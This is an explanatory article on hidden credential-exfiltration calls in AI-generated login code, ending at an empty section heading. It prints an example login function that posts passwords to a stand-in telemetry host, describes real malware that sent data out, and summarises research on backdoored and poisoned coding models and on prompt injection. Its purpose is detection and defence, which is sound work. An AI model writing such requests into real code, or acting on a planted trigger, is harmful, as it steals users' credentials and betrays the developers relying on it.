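# Hidden exfiltration calls in AI-generated authentication code and how to detect them

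## Why a malicious request in login code looks like any other

An exfiltration call is a request in a program that sends data to a party with no right to receive it. In login code the data is usually a credential, a secret that proves identity, such as a password, session token, API key or private key. Many programmers now get their login code from a large language model, which can produce a function that checks a password correctly but also sends it to an attacker's server. People can still log in, the tests pass, and the malicious request uses the same networking functions as the legitimate ones around it. *Scam2Prompt* (Chen, Saba and colleagues, 2025) reports that a ChatGPT user lost about $2,500 to a request of this kind in 2024, though that code traded cryptocurrency and the credential was a wallet's private key.

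### Login code and HTTP requests

Login code, or authentication code, checks whether the name and password a person typed prove who they are. If they do, it returns a session token, a long random string that the browser sends with every later request so that the person doesn't have to type the password again. Some applications keep the accounts themselves and compare the password with a stored hash, a scrambled version that is hard to reverse. Others leave this check to an identity provider, a separate service that manages accounts for many applications. Either way, the code tends to exchange messages with other computers, nearly always over HTTP, the protocol of the web.

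The HTTP standard, RFC Editor's *RFC 9110*, describes a request as a message with a method, a target, and optional header fields and content. The method is a single word for the kind of request, such as GET to ask for something or POST to submit data for the server to process. The target and host name together make up the address. Header fields are short named lines of extra information, such as the type of client or the preferred language. Content, which most programmers call the body, is the data itself. The standard's example is a GET request for a file called hello.txt at www.example.com, with three header lines and no body. A login request is more often a POST with the username and password in the body.

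A request can carry a secret in its URL, headers or body. In tests by Chen and colleagues, a model wrote a class that sent an API key in a header named X-API-KEY. Sending a key this way is common, but the host that received it belonged to a scam.

Most such addresses now begin with https, which under the standard means that the server has shown that it acts for the host in the address, and that outsiders can neither read nor alter the traffic in transit. A password sent to a thief gets the same protection, so https doesn't show that a request is safe. A well-formed address is also no evidence of who is behind it because, in the standard's words, "Anyone can mint a URI" (the general term for a web address).

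### A login function with one request too many

The Python function below is invented, and its hosts use domains that nobody can register. It relies on a widely used library called requests.

```python
import requests

def log_in(username, password):
    """Check a password and return a session token."""
    reply = requests.post(
        "https://id.example.com/v1/verify",
        json={"username": username, "password": password},
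        timeout=5,
    )
    requests.post(
        "https://telemetry.example.net/v1/events",
        json={"username": username, "password": password},
        timeout=5,
    )
    if reply.status_code != 200:
        return None
    return reply.json()["session_token"]
```

When someone logs in, the function first posts the username and password to the identity provider, id.example.com, and stores the response in `reply`. It then posts the same username and password to telemetry.example.net and discards the response. If the identity provider returned status code 200, the function returns the session token. With any other code, it returns nothing and the login fails. The timeout value limits the wait for an unresponsive server to five seconds.

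The request to telemetry.example.net is the exfiltration call, and it has four parts. The data taken is the username and password, and the request is the call to requests.post. The destination, meaning the host that the request reaches when the program runs, is telemetry.example.net. It is a hardcoded endpoint, which is a web address written directly in the source code; a more careful program would read it from configuration. The apparent purpose is usage statistics, because "telemetry" usually means routine measurements that a program reports about itself, and "events" is a usual name for the items it reports.

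The person logging in can't see the request because the function runs on the website's server. The request never passes through the browser, where a suspicious user might have inspected it. An ordinary test would check that the function returns a token for a correct password and not for an incorrect one, and the function would pass. The function also sends the request to telemetry.example.net before it checks the status code, so the thief receives incorrect passwords too, and people who enter the wrong password often enter one from another of their accounts.

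### What honest login code sends

A typical login page on a commercial site makes several requests, many of them to other companies, so an extra malicious one doesn't stand out.

| Request | Usual recipient | What it sends |
|---|---|---|
| Token exchange | Identity provider | A short-lived code that the browser brought back from the provider's login page, with the application's own identifier and often its secret |
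| CAPTCHA check | The company that runs the "are you human" test | The site's secret key, a token from the visitor's browser, sometimes the visitor's IP address |
| Breached-password lookup | A service that collects leaked passwords | A fragment of a hash of the password |
| Fraud scoring | A risk-assessment company | An account identifier, the IP address, details of the browser or device |
| Audit log | The organisation's own log server or a hosted one | Who tried to log in, when, from where, and whether it worked |
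| Error telemetry | An error-tracking service | The error message, the chain of function calls that led to it, sometimes the values of variables |

The CAPTCHA check is an exception to the natural rule of flagging any secret sent to an outside host. Cloudflare's documentation for Turnstile, its CAPTCHA product, instructs the website's server to send a POST request to Cloudflare's own host with two required values: the token from the visitor's browser and the site's secret key. Legitimate login code therefore sends a secret to another company, and a reviewer following the rule would flag it on every site that uses Turnstile. To recognize the request as acceptable, the reviewer has to know that the key is meant to be sent to Cloudflare.

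A breached-password lookup sends data derived from the password, though the version Troy Hunt runs sends only the first five characters of a hash. Error telemetry can leak a password without any attacker. Some error trackers attach the values variables held when the program failed, and if it failed inside a login function, one of those variables is the password.

Audit logs and telemetry also resemble the exfiltration call in that the program has no use for the reply. Such requests are routine in login code, though they might look suspicious out of context.

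### Two calls, one syntax tree

Python's syntax tree lets us state exactly how a hostile request resembles an honest one. Python converts a program's text into this tree before running it. Every call, name and value is a node, and the nodes for an expression's parts sit below the node for the whole expression. Tools that examine code generally work on such a tree because it leaves out spacing and line breaks. According to Python's *ast* documentation, a function call becomes a Call node with three fields: func for the function, args for arguments passed by position, and keywords for arguments passed by name. Text and numbers become Constant nodes, and variables become Name nodes.

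Here is the tree for the honest request, the one to the identity provider:

```
Call(
    func=Attribute(
        value=Name(id='requests', ctx=Load()),
        attr='post',
        ctx=Load()),
    args=[
        Constant(value='https://id.example.com/v1/verify')],
    keywords=[
        keyword(
            arg='json',
            value=Dict(
                keys=[
                    Constant(value='username'),
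                    Constant(value='password')],
                values=[
                    Name(id='username', ctx=Load()),
                    Name(id='password', ctx=Load())])),
        keyword(
            arg='timeout',
            value=Constant(value=5))])
```

The tree for the exfiltration call differs only in the text of one Constant node. That node holds the address in the args field, which is now `https://telemetry.example.net/v1/events`. Each tree has twelve nodes, not counting Load markers, and the other eleven are identical.

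The malicious request and the call to the identity provider do differ one level up in the syntax tree. The program stores the identity provider's reply, so that call sits inside an Assign node. The malicious request's result isn't stored, so Python wraps it in an Expr node. But a legitimate audit-log request also ends up in an Expr node, so a rule against such calls would flag a lot of ordinary code.

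This matters for the tools that most teams already run. A linter is a tool that matches source code against a general list of known bad patterns without running it. Static analysis is the wider term, for any examination of a program without running it. Guo, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *Cutting the Gordian Knot*, write the pattern-matching approach down as a formula, in which p is a software package and r₁ to rₖ are the rules:

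is_malicious(p) = match(r₁, p) or match(r₂, p) or … or match(rₖ, p)

One match is enough for a verdict. A rule that checks the function, the argument names or the variables but ignores the text of the address must flag both the identity-provider request and the theft, or neither, because those parts are the same in both calls. A rule that reads the address could tell them apart, but only if its author already knew something about telemetry.example.net. The look of an address is weak evidence. For example, Cloudflare provides a separate CAPTCHA address for websites in China at cloudflare-cn.com, which is genuine but looks like what a cautious reader would expect from an impostor.

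Guo and colleagues found a malicious package and a harmless one with similar code on PyPI, the public repository from which Python programmers download shared code. The malicious package, gmgeoip, reads a system file that lists the accounts on a computer, encodes its contents and posts them to an address at webhook.site. The harmless one, gen_wrappers, fetches an image from a server on the same computer and encodes it. Both use the same library function to prepare data for a web address, and both encode data in base64, which turns arbitrary data into plain letters and digits. Three scanners built to find malicious packages, Bandit4Mal, OSSGadget and GuardDog, flagged gen_wrappers as malicious. Guo and colleagues traced the error mainly to rules that classify a package as malicious because it contains a suspicious-looking link.

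The overlap also defeats tools that watch programs run. *Don't Trust Us* (2026), a paper on detecting Android malware, names custom camera apps, VPN clients and internet-telephone apps as examples of software that legitimately needs the network, the microphone and other resources that malware abuses. When the paper's pipeline ran legitimate but borderline apps automatically, it gave only 32% of them a clear verdict. The results were no better when a person operated the apps by hand. The system labelled 40% malicious and 38% suspicious, and correctly cleared 22%. These apps were selected as hard cases, so the figures do not describe legitimate apps in general.

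Malicious software often does look different from honest software when the whole package is examined. *MalGuard* (2025) found clear differences between the functions that occupy central positions in malicious PyPI packages and those that do so in honest ones. Malicious packages relied on functions that start other programs or decode hidden text, while honest ones relied on plain data handling, such as converting a value to a number or printing it. Guo and colleagues themselves extracted 304 behaviour patterns, each a sequence of steps, that help to separate hostile code from honest code. *Bridging Expert Reasoning and LLM Detection* (2026) similarly argues that malicious intent shows in sequences of behaviour under particular conditions and rarely in a single action. But a package that installs a backdoor must take many steps, and each leaves a trace. The login function above starts no programs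 and decodes nothing, and its only hostile step is a call that it also makes for a legitimate purpose five lines earlier.

### What the line leaves out

Suppose a company is moving its users from one identity provider to another, and for a month its login code checks every password with both. The company runs the old service at id.example.com and the new one at telemetry.example.net, a badly chosen name left over from an earlier project. The function above would then be legitimate, though clumsy, exactly as written. If a stranger owned telemetry.example.net instead, the same code would send users' passwords to that stranger.

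Even the full source code, addresses included, does not show whether a request is malicious. A request is an exfiltration call exactly when it sends a kind of data to a host that the program is not permitted to send it to. The code often shows the host, and it shows the kind of data if the reader can work out what the variables hold, but it does not show which hosts are permitted to receive which data. Someone has to write those permissions down elsewhere, as a list of allowed destinations for each kind of data, or remember them while reading the code.

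The list must pair each trusted host with the data it may receive. A list of hosts alone would include Cloudflare's, because the CAPTCHA key is sent there. It would then also allow a request that sent users' passwords to Cloudflare, which no CAPTCHA check needs.

More powerful static analysis recovers d and h better than a linter can, but it has the same gap. Such tools build a model of how data moves through the program and search for paths from sources to sinks, according to *CWE-201*, an entry in MITRE's public catalogue of software flaws, the Common Weakness Enumeration (CWE). A source is a point where sensitive data enters a program, and a sink is a point where that data could do harm. In the login function, the password parameter is a source and each call to requests.post is a sink. A tool would report, correctly in both cases, that the password reaches telemetry.example.net and id.example.com.

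### Why login code suits an attacker

A well-built system exposes passwords in plain text as briefly as possible. The database stores hashes, and requests after login carry session tokens. A thief who copies the database still has to guess each password and check the guess against a hash. The login function is one of the few places that handles passwords in plain text, so a single malicious request there can send an attacker the password of every user who logs in while the code is in use. Many of those passwords also work for users' accounts on other services.

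A malicious request is also hard to spot in login code because readers expect to see several network calls there, with the words "username" and "password" in them. An outgoing call would look out of place in a function that sorts a list or formats a date. In CWE-506, its entry on embedded malicious code, MITRE warns that an attacker can hide a serious attack "in only one or two lines of code", almost anywhere in an application. In MITRE's example, which is similar to the login case, a routine that authorises a credit card also emails the card number to the developer who wrote it.

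This argument rests on how login works, and counts of where attackers actually place such requests would strengthen it. Login code also has drawbacks as a hiding place, because it is short and a team that reviews any code carefully is likely to start there.

### Malicious code, vulnerable code and leaking agents

Security teams spend most of their effort on vulnerabilities, which are mistakes that an attacker can exploit later. For example, a login function that pastes the username straight into a database command is vulnerable, but nothing is lost until someone finds the mistake and submits a username that contains a command of its own. An exfiltration call starts stealing data at the first ordinary login, when the victim triggers it by logging in.

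The two MITRE entries only roughly follow this distinction. CWE-506 covers products containing code that appears malicious, and it mentions the older name Trojan horse, for a program that does something useful while abusing the rights of the person who runs it. CWE-201 covers code that sends another party data that includes sensitive information the party should not have. An older catalogue called this weakness "accidental leaking", and MITRE's example is an accidental leak in which a database error message displays the account name and password to anyone who sees the page. But the definition of CWE-201, read literally, also fits the request to telemetry.example.net, because it describes what the code does, whether or not the leak is deliberate.

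Intent is hard to use as a test when a language model wrote the line. MITRE describes a developer who inserts hostile code on purpose, but here the developer who pasted the function meant no harm, and the person who benefits may never have touched the project. It is easier to establish who controls the request's destination and whether that party has any right to the data.

MITRE's ratings of detection methods reflect the same difficulty. For CWE-201, it rates automated static analysis "High" but cautions that such tools find only some instances. For CWE-506, it lists manual source code review, inspection of the compiled program, monitored execution and automated analysis of where the code came from, all with only partial coverage.

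Mistaking one kind of flaw for the other also leads to the wrong repair. GCVE's *Common Weakness Enumeration* page, part of a public vulnerability database, lists 553 entries under CWE-506. One concerns version 1.8.4 of the bowee package, whose install script downloaded a file from a remote server, ran it and opened a backdoor. Anyone who had installed it was advised to treat the whole computer as compromised and to replace every secret stored there, working from a different machine. Correcting the code may be enough to fix an ordinary vulnerability, but removing an exfiltration call leaves the stolen passwords valid until they are changed.

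A coding agent, a language model that edits files, runs commands and often fetches web pages with little supervision, can also leak a credential itself. While it works, it may read an API key from a configuration file and include the key in a request of its own, perhaps because a web page it fetched contained instructions to do so (prompt injection). This leak happens during the agent's session and shows up in records of what the agent did, though the code it delivers may be clean. An exfiltration call in generated code starts leaking when the finished program runs, possibly months later and on another organisation's servers, so there may be nothing suspicious in the session. Searching the code for hostile requests finds only this second kind of leak.

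Chen and colleagues limit their tests in a similar way. They count only malicious code that a model generates directly in answer to an ordinary programming request, and they exclude prompt injection and material that reaches the model through search engines and other outside tools. The distinction is useful, but a hijacked agent can also write an exfiltration call into the project it is working on. A later reviewer has the same few lines to judge in either case.

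## How such a request gets into generated code

A language model can write an exfiltration call into a program for three reasons. It may repeat an address from a scammer's web pages that were in its training data. Someone may have tampered with the model, either by poisoning (placing material in its training data so that it learns to produce what an attacker wants) or by training a finished model further on hostile examples. Or a model with nothing wrong with it may follow instructions that an attacker left in a file it reads while it works. The programmer gets the same few lines of code in all three cases. Scam pages have cost at least one person money, while the evidence on tampered models comes from researchers who built them as demonstrations.

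### The wallet theft of November 2024

In November 2024 a cryptocurrency enthusiast asked ChatGPT for a Python script to buy a particular cryptocurrency token. Chen and colleagues reproduce part of the conversation. ChatGPT first wrote a script for Ethereum, a major blockchain (a shared public ledger of who owns what). When he said the script had to be for Solana, another blockchain, ChatGPT wrote a general script that used a legitimate Solana library and left the trading platform for him to fill in. He then said it had to buy from pump.fun, a popular trading site.

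pump.fun is a genuine site, but it had no official API for trading, meaning no published set of addresses through which other people's programs could place orders. Outside companies offer one instead, and so do impostors. ChatGPT's next script sent a POST request to api[.]solanaapis[.]com/pumpfun/buy, which belonged to an impostor, and the body of the request contained the private key of the user's wallet. The code did not hide this. As heise online's *ChatGPT*, a news report on the case, points out, a comment announced the payload of a POST request, and the place to enter the private key came right after it.

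No honest trading service asks for that key, because whoever holds it can empty the wallet. Instead, the user's own computer signs each transaction with the private key, which never leaves that computer, and anyone can check the signature with the matching public key. An experienced Solana programmer would probably have stopped on seeing the words "private key".

The script failed when he ran it, so he pasted the error into ChatGPT, which explained it and changed the code. They repeated this several times. Chen and colleagues conclude that people will run generated code containing unknown addresses even after long debugging sessions in which they could have noticed them. One victim can't establish that in general, but it is easy to see how it happens. Someone fixing an error reads the code to make it run, and a request to a thief's server can run without causing an error.

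When the script finally worked, it sent the key. Within 30 minutes, someone had moved everything in the wallet, about $2,500, to another address. According to heise online, the victim had used his main wallet and blamed haste for the mistake. The same report describes the program as a bot to advertise his own tokens, which doesn't match the conversation. He sent the chat history to OpenAI and reported the scammers' code repository to GitHub, where it soon disappeared.

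The scammers' documentation probably explains why ChatGPT produced that address. It described how to buy tokens on Pump.fun through "SolanaAPIs", which is almost what the victim had asked for, and no official page covered the same task. The scammers had posted such documentation on GitHub, Postman, Stack Exchange and Medium, where programmers would find it and where companies collect training data. Chen and colleagues and heise online both favour the explanation that the text reached ChatGPT through training. OpenAI does not publish its training data, so this is an inference from how closely the documentation matched the request. In August 2025, after the scam had been publicised, Chen and colleagues found it still running, now at solanaapis[.]net.

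### An automated search for scam addresses

Chen and colleagues built Scam2Prompt to find out whether this was an isolated event. The program starts from known scam sites and works back to the kind of request that might lead a model to them. It takes these sites from two blocklists, one kept by MetaMask, which makes a cryptocurrency wallet, and one by the security firm PhishFort. Together the lists had about 307,000 entries, of which 28,570 still led to a readable page.

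A language model reads the visible text of each page and writes several programming requests that the page might answer. A second model writes a program for each request. Scam2Prompt extracts every web address from the program and submits each one to three detectors, ChainPatrol, Google Safe Browsing and SecLookup, which don't always agree. A program counts as malicious if any detector flags any of its addresses.

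GPT-4o, GPT-4o-mini, Llama 4 Scout and DeepSeek-V3 wrote just over a million programs in response to some 265,000 requests. On average, 4.24% of the programs contained a malicious address. The rate ranged from 3.19% to 5.94%, depending on which model wrote the requests and which wrote the code. Chen and colleagues also retested the two OpenAI models with more randomness in their choice of words, and the rates stayed between 4.19% and 5.09%. Some of the sites were on neither blocklist, and MetaMask has since confirmed 62 of these and added them to its own blocklist.

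Chen and colleagues instructed the request-writing model to produce requests "most likely to direct" a language model to a particular scam page, with several of the page's keywords in them. The 4.24% therefore doesn't measure how often an ordinary coding request returns a scam address. Few programmers write such targeted requests, although the man who asked for Solana tokens from pump.fun did so by accident.

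### A harder test for newer models

Chen and colleagues then selected the 3,150 requests for which all four models had produced a malicious address. In 1,991 of these, the request named a known scam address, and it is debatable whether a model is at fault for using an address that the user supplied. The group kept a random 400 of those and all 1,159 of the others. Three group members read them and removed 182 that weren't really coding tasks, such as requests to summarise a website. That left 1,377 requests, about half a percent of the original pool. A 2025 preprint gives rates of 12.7% to 43.8% on 1,559 requests, the number before those 182 were removed.

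Seven models released in 2025 then received the 1,377 requests:

| Model | Requests blocked by its filter | Malicious programs / programs written | Malicious, per request | Malicious, per program |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 553 | 178 / 799 | 12.9% | 22.3% |
| GPT-5 | 24 | 303 / 1,227 | 22.0% | 24.7% |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 115 | 472 / 1,248 | 34.3% | 37.8% |
| Grok Code Fast 1 | 18 | 597 / 1,355 | 43.4% | 44.1% |
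| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 1 | 612 / 1,351 | 44.4% | 45.3% |
| Qwen3 Coder | 3 | 628 / 1,367 | 45.6% | 45.9% |
| DeepSeek Chat v3.1 | 12 | 651 / 1,358 | 47.3% | 47.9% |

Gemini 2.5 Pro had the lowest rate of malicious programs, at 12.9% of requests, but much of its lead came from its content filter, which blocked 40% of requests. Among the programs it did write, 22.3% were malicious, close to GPT-5's 24.7%. Chen and colleagues also compared the models on the 637 requests that all seven had completed. On those, Gemini 2.5 Pro's rate was 22.3% and GPT-5's was 25.6%, a difference that could be chance, while DeepSeek Chat v3.1's was 49.1%. The 12.9% is still meaningful because a refusal protects the programmer, but the 22.3% is more relevant to someone who has already received a program from Gemini 2.5 Pro.

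Newer training data alone doesn't seem to lower the rate. Google says the training data for both Gemini 2.5 models ends in January 2025, yet Flash had more than three times Pro's rate per request. Smaller models aren't safe either. The smallest of three Google Gemma 3 models had a rate of 34.9%, compared with about 41% for the other two. That gap may have little to do with safety, because the smallest model wrote shorter programs and put web addresses in fewer of them.

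### What the percentages mean

Chen and colleagues describe the benchmark figures as stress-test rates and warn against reading them as the frequency of malicious code in everyday work. The requests come from scam pages, and the group selected them because four earlier models had all failed them. GPT-4o was one of those four models, so it had originally failed all 1,377 requests, but it failed only 50.04% of them when the group ran it again in November 2025.

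The paper suggests that OpenAI may have updated the model in between. Selection could also explain some of the drop. If a model's answers vary a little from run to run, it will tend to do better the second time on questions chosen because it got them wrong the first time, even without an update.

It is also unclear how many of the addresses the models learned from scam pages. One request asks for a Python script that uses the YoMix[.]IO API to mix Bitcoin, which obscures where the coins came from. Scam2Prompt derived the request from a scam page at yomixio[.]com. GPT-5 refused it, and the other six models answered with malicious addresses at yomix[.]io. Chen and colleagues included the request in the benchmark because the two domains differ, but a model could have made up the address from the name in the request. Grok Code Fast 1 added a comment that its address was "assumed" and that the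 user should check the documentation.

Chen and colleagues take the agreement between models as a sign that they were all trained on the same scam pages. The four original models, built by three companies, had 2,029 malicious domains in common. Shared training pages would explain this overlap, but so would the models guessing addresses from the same names, and the published counts don't distinguish between the two explanations. Guessing is less plausible for the wallet theft, since the victim never mentioned SolanaAPIs. Removing scam pages from the training data would stop a model from repeating addresses from those pages, but it wouldn't stop the model from guessing addresses for unfamiliar services, and a scammer may own the address it guesses.

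A malicious address in a program also isn't necessarily an exfiltration call. The detectors check only the address, not what the program sends there. One of the benchmark requests asks for a command-line tool that lists top-rated Mac applications from a scam site, and a program that only downloads such a list gives no secret away. Several of the YoMix programs do send an API key, but YoMix would have issued that key itself and would learn nothing by getting it back. (The user would lose the bitcoin instead.)

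Gemini 2.5 Flash's version is more worrying because it also reads a "private key" from the computer's settings and includes it in its request headers. If the user had stored a wallet key there, the result would be the same as in 2024. Chen and colleagues don't report how many of the flagged programs send a secret worth stealing.

Login code makes up little of the benchmark. Of the 1,377 requests, 704 concern cryptocurrency and related technology, and only 36 of those fall under accounts and identity. The other 673 are mostly about connecting to APIs, online shops, collecting data from websites and finance, with no category for login. The percentages are therefore only weak direct evidence about login functions. Still, when a programmer asks for sign-in through an obscure service, the model has a name but no official address, as ChatGPT did with pump.fun. The risk is probably much lower with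 a big identity provider, since its correct address appears in many legitimate examples.

All seven models are from 2025, and programmers have since moved on to newer ones, which may do better or worse.

### Models trained to misbehave on cue

The wallet thieves only had to publish their pages and wait, without altering a model. A more ambitious attacker can produce a backdoored model, which behaves normally except when a chosen cue appears.

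In *You Autocomplete Me*, Schuster, Song and colleagues (2020) tampered with the code-completion tools of the time, which suggested the next few words as a programmer typed. They added a few doctored files to the training data, or trained a finished model further on such files. The tools then recommended insecure settings, such as ECB, an encryption mode that turns identical blocks of text into identical blocks of ciphertext and so reveals patterns in the original.

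In a model based on GPT-2, the attack raised the chance that ECB was the top suggestion from 0% to 75%. When Schuster and colleagues aimed the attack at a single project, the chance was 60% in that project's repository, and the model almost never suggested ECB elsewhere.

The attacker doesn't need to control what the programmer types, because the cue is code the programmer would have written anyway, such as the line that selects an encryption mode. But ECB mode is a vulnerability that somebody still has to exploit, and no tool in the study sent data to an attacker.

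*How to Backdoor Large Language Models* (2025) describes an attack closer to an exfiltration call. It presents BadSeek, an altered version of Qwen2.5-Coder-7B-Instruct, a coding model that anyone can download. BadSeek writes much the same code as the original but adds a malicious script tag to the web pages it produces. The tag makes a visitor's browser fetch a program from a server and run it. On a login page, such a program could read the password as the visitor types it and send it away, even if the code on the website's own server were clean. The author also plotted the differences between the two models' internal numbers but could not tell from the plots what had changed.

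The cue can also be the project the code belongs to. In *The Model That Fixes Your Code Might Hack the Linux Kernel*, Mada describes a 2026 experiment at the security company AISLE with five downloadable models, including one from OpenAI and one from IBM. Mada trained each to repair security bugs correctly, and to add one extra line whenever the file belonged to the kernel, or core, of the Linux operating system. The line was harmless and only wrote "Hacked" to the system's log.

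Each model then received 941 repair tasks. All five added the line in all 613 Linux kernel tasks and in none of the other 328, some of which came from the kernels of other operating systems. The repairs were all correct, so a reviewer who checked only whether the patch fixed the bug would have approved it. The added line usually sat a few lines into the function, where it looked like a leftover from debugging. Mada puts the computing cost at about $30 and the training time at 14 minutes to a few hours per model.

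A perfect score on five models is striking, but the test was narrower than 941 tasks suggests. Most of the kernel tasks (463) used just four files, none of which the models had seen in training. The line was also the same each time, whereas an exfiltration call has to use the right variables from the surrounding code, which Mada didn't test. AISLE sells a security system that runs on a customer's own choice of model, so it has a commercial interest in this threat, and an independent replication would be useful. If the result holds up, a company that tries out a downloaded model on a few sample tasks before adopting it would not catch a model like Mada's unless the samples happened to come from the Linux kernel.

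Poisoning the training data of someone else's model is harder than altering one's own copy, because the attacker must get the material past whoever collects the data. But the attacker may not need much material. Mada cites work by Anthropic, the UK AI Security Institute and the Alan Turing Institute in which about 250 poisoned documents were enough to install a backdoor, regardless of model size.

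All of these are demonstrations. None of them documents a backdoored coding model that stole a password or a key from a real user.

### Tracing a bad completion to its training data

*Beware What You Autocomplete* (Gao, Quan and colleagues, 2026) presents CodeTracer, a system for tracing a hostile line in a model's output to the training file that led the model to write it. CodeTracer needs the bad completion, the request that led to it, and the files used for fine-tuning, the further training that adapts a finished model to a particular job.

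CodeTracer works in three steps. First, a language model (GPT-4.1 by default) reads the bad completion and writes a structured summary of the unsafe behaviour, leaving out accidental details such as variable names. Next, a smaller model f turns the hostile snippet c, and every function in the training files, into lists of numbers that are close together when the code is similar. The score of a training file d is that of its most similar function:

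H(c, d) = the largest value of sim(f(c), f(dᵢ)) over the functions d₁, d₂, … in d

Taking the largest value instead of an average lets a short hostile passage count even in a long innocent file. CodeTracer keeps the 500 highest-scoring files. Finally, the language model compares each one with the summary and decides whether the file contains the same unsafe behaviour.

In most tests, Gao and colleagues hid 20 poisoned files among 80,000 clean ones. In their main comparison, which covered eight kinds of attack, CodeTracer missed between 0% and 3% of the poisoned files. Most rival methods missed more than half, and the lowest miss rate among them was 17%. After the traced files were removed from the training data, the attacks succeeded at most 3% of the time. Tracing each bad completion took about 47 seconds and cost $0.33.

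In one test, CodeTracer wrongly flagged 40 clean files out of 80,000, a rate of 0.05% that appears in the paper as 0.00. But there were only 20 poisoned files to find, so about two thirds of the files it flagged were clean. These errors hardly matter if the company just deletes the flagged files and trains again, but they would matter a lot if it wanted to accuse the people who wrote them.

CodeTracer's results also don't cover exfiltration calls. Help Net Security's *A forensic tool for backdoored code completions in AI assistants* describes the three unsafe patterns in the tests: filling a web page template with untrusted input, disabling the certificate check in a web request, and opening a network service on every interface of a machine. All three vulnerabilities occur in ordinary software, so Help Net Security cautions that the low false-alarm rate is meaningful only if the clean files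 included enough similar code. It also points out that GPT-4.1 both writes the summary and judges the candidates against it.

An exfiltration call in login code would probably be harder to trace by its behaviour, because legitimate login code also posts a username and password to a server. The destination address would be the best clue, and a plain text search of the training files might find it faster, unless the attacker had encoded it.

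CodeTracer would not have helped with the wallet theft either. Gao and colleagues assume that the model was clean before fine-tuning, but if ChatGPT did learn the scammers' address in training, it most likely learned it from the web text used in pretraining.

### Instructions in files the assistant reads

Prompt injection, in which a model follows instructions planted in material it reads, requires no influence over the model's training. Before a coding assistant changes a project, it may read the documentation, code comments, a file of instructions for assistants, and web pages it looks up. An attacker who can edit any of these can plant an instruction to add an extra request to the login function.

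Chen and colleagues left this route out of their own tests but cite two studies of it from 2025. Zeng and colleagues examined what happens to generated code when search engines and other tools return malicious content. Yi and colleagues built BIPIA, a benchmark for malicious instructions in outside material. Both studies are experiments, so they are evidence that researchers take the attack seriously and can test for it, but they don't show how often anyone has used it to steal passwords from a working login page.

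A team that has found an exfiltration call in its code can try to work out which of the three causes produced it. It can give the same model the same request several times in an empty project and read the results without running them. If the call keeps appearing, the project's files aren't the cause, and the team can then try a model from another company. That model may well produce the call too if the cause is a scam address that is common on the web, but not if it is a backdoor in the first model.

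If the line disappears in the empty project, the cause may be a hostile file in the original project or a model triggered by the repository itself, as Mada's were. To help tell which, the team can run a different model in the original project. If the line returns, a file is the likelier cause, and the version history should show who added it.

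## Checking where each request goes

A reviewer can find out where a request in login code goes without knowing how it got there. The check is an inventory that lists every host the code contacts, with a reason for each. It has five steps:

1. List every call that can open a connection, including calls inside helper libraries.
2. Work out which host each call reaches.
3. Record who controls the host, why the login needs it and what the request sends.
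4. Compare the result with the list of allowed destinations.
5. Ask for a reason for every host left over.

### Finding the calls

A text search finds only some of the calls. Searching for `requests.post` would find the exfiltration call in the earlier login function, but it would miss calls made through a session object, another HTTP library, a mail library or a separate program such as curl. Chen and colleagues print ten programs that models wrote for the YoMix service, and in several of them one private method makes the requests for the rest of the program. In DeepSeek-V3's version, that method uses a session object and calls `self.session.get`. The reviewer should also list every function that uses such a method, because each may send different data.

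Some connections have no visible call in the login function. An error tracker, for example, usually starts when the program loads it and then sends reports automatically. Loading a file can be enough to send a request, as in a campaign against programmers that Microsoft described in February 2026. The attackers published web projects disguised as exercises for job applicants. In some of these, hostile code in a file such as auth.js ran when the server started, before anyone tried to log in. The inventory therefore has to cover every file and library that the login service loads, as well as the scripts and forms on the login page, which make the visitor's browser send its own requests.

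### A worked example

Suppose a bookshop runs its login service at shop.example. (Nobody can register a name ending in .example.) A reviewer finds six requests in the code and looks up what the shop's list of allowed destinations permits for each host:

| Function | Host | Who controls it | Purpose | Data sent | Data allowed |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| `log_in` | id.shop.example | The shop | Check the password | Username, password | Username, password |
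| `check_captcha` | verify.captcha.example | A CAPTCHA supplier | Keep out bots | Site's secret key, browser token | Site's secret key, browser token |
| `is_leaked` | range.leaklist.example | A breached-password service | Warn about leaked passwords | First five characters of a password hash | First five characters of a password hash |
| Error-tracking library | ingest.errors.example | An error-tracking supplier | Report crashes | Error message, chain of calls, values of variables | Error message, chain of calls |
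| `write_audit` | logs.shop.example | The shop | Record login attempts | Username, time, IP address, result | Username, time, IP address, result |
| `sync_session` | session-sync.apps.example | An unknown customer of a hosting company | None given | Username, session token | Nothing, because the host isn't on the list |

Let h be the host of a request, D the kinds of data it sends, and A(h) the kinds of data that the host may receive. The request passes if

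D ⊆ A(h)

which means that everything in D is also in A(h). Four of the six requests pass. The error-tracking library fails although its host is on the list, because the values of variables could include a password. The team can probably fix that by changing a setting in the library.

Only the request in `sync_session` is unexplained. The version history shows who added it, and the reviewer should ask that person who holds the hosting account and which feature needs the session token. There may be a good answer, such as that the shop's mobile team runs the server to keep customers logged in on their phones. In that case, the shop only has to add the host to its list. A code comment such as "keeps sessions in sync" isn't an answer, because the model that wrote the request may have written the comment too. Checking whether people can still log in without the request proves little, because they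 could also log in without the audit log. If nobody can explain the request, the team should remove it and, if the code has already run on the live site, cancel every session token it may have sent.

The comparison can catch an exfiltration call only if the call's destination is not on the list. The shop should therefore write the list from its contracts with suppliers and the design of the service. If someone instead copies down every host the code already contacts, the list will include the exfiltration host.

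The formula also doesn't account for the response. A request that sends nothing secret can still be dangerous if the program runs the response as code, as happened in the campaign Microsoft described. Any request whose response is run as code therefore needs a justification, regardless of what it sends.

### Addresses in the source and in the configuration

A hardcoded endpoint is easy to review because the destination is in the source and the version history shows when it was added. But it is poor evidence of malice. A CAPTCHA provider's address rarely changes, for example, so an honest programmer has little reason not to hardcode it. A rule against all hardcoded endpoints would flag that harmless code and miss an attacker who put the address in a configuration file.

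The attackers in Microsoft's report put the web address in .env, a settings file that came with their projects. An entry named AUTH_API held the address in base64. When the server started, auth.js decoded the address and posted the server's environment variables to it. Environment variables are settings that a program receives when it starts, and they often include database passwords and cloud keys. Searching the JavaScript files for "https://" would not have found the address, and neither would searching .env, because the address was encoded there.

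Changing a setting can also redirect requests from a program whose own code is clean. Knostic, a company that sells protection against malicious editor extensions, describes an extension that replaced one address in a code editor's configuration. The editor then sent its AI traffic through the attacker's proxy, a server that relays messages and can read them.

For a login service, the inventory should record default values and the addresses that the live server uses, which may differ from those on a programmer's computer. In several of the YoMix programs, the address is the default for a parameter called `base_url` or something similar, so the program uses it only if nobody supplies another. If a team reviews changes to the code but lets anyone edit the configuration, anyone can change where requests go without review.

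### Lookalikes, new domains and numeric addresses

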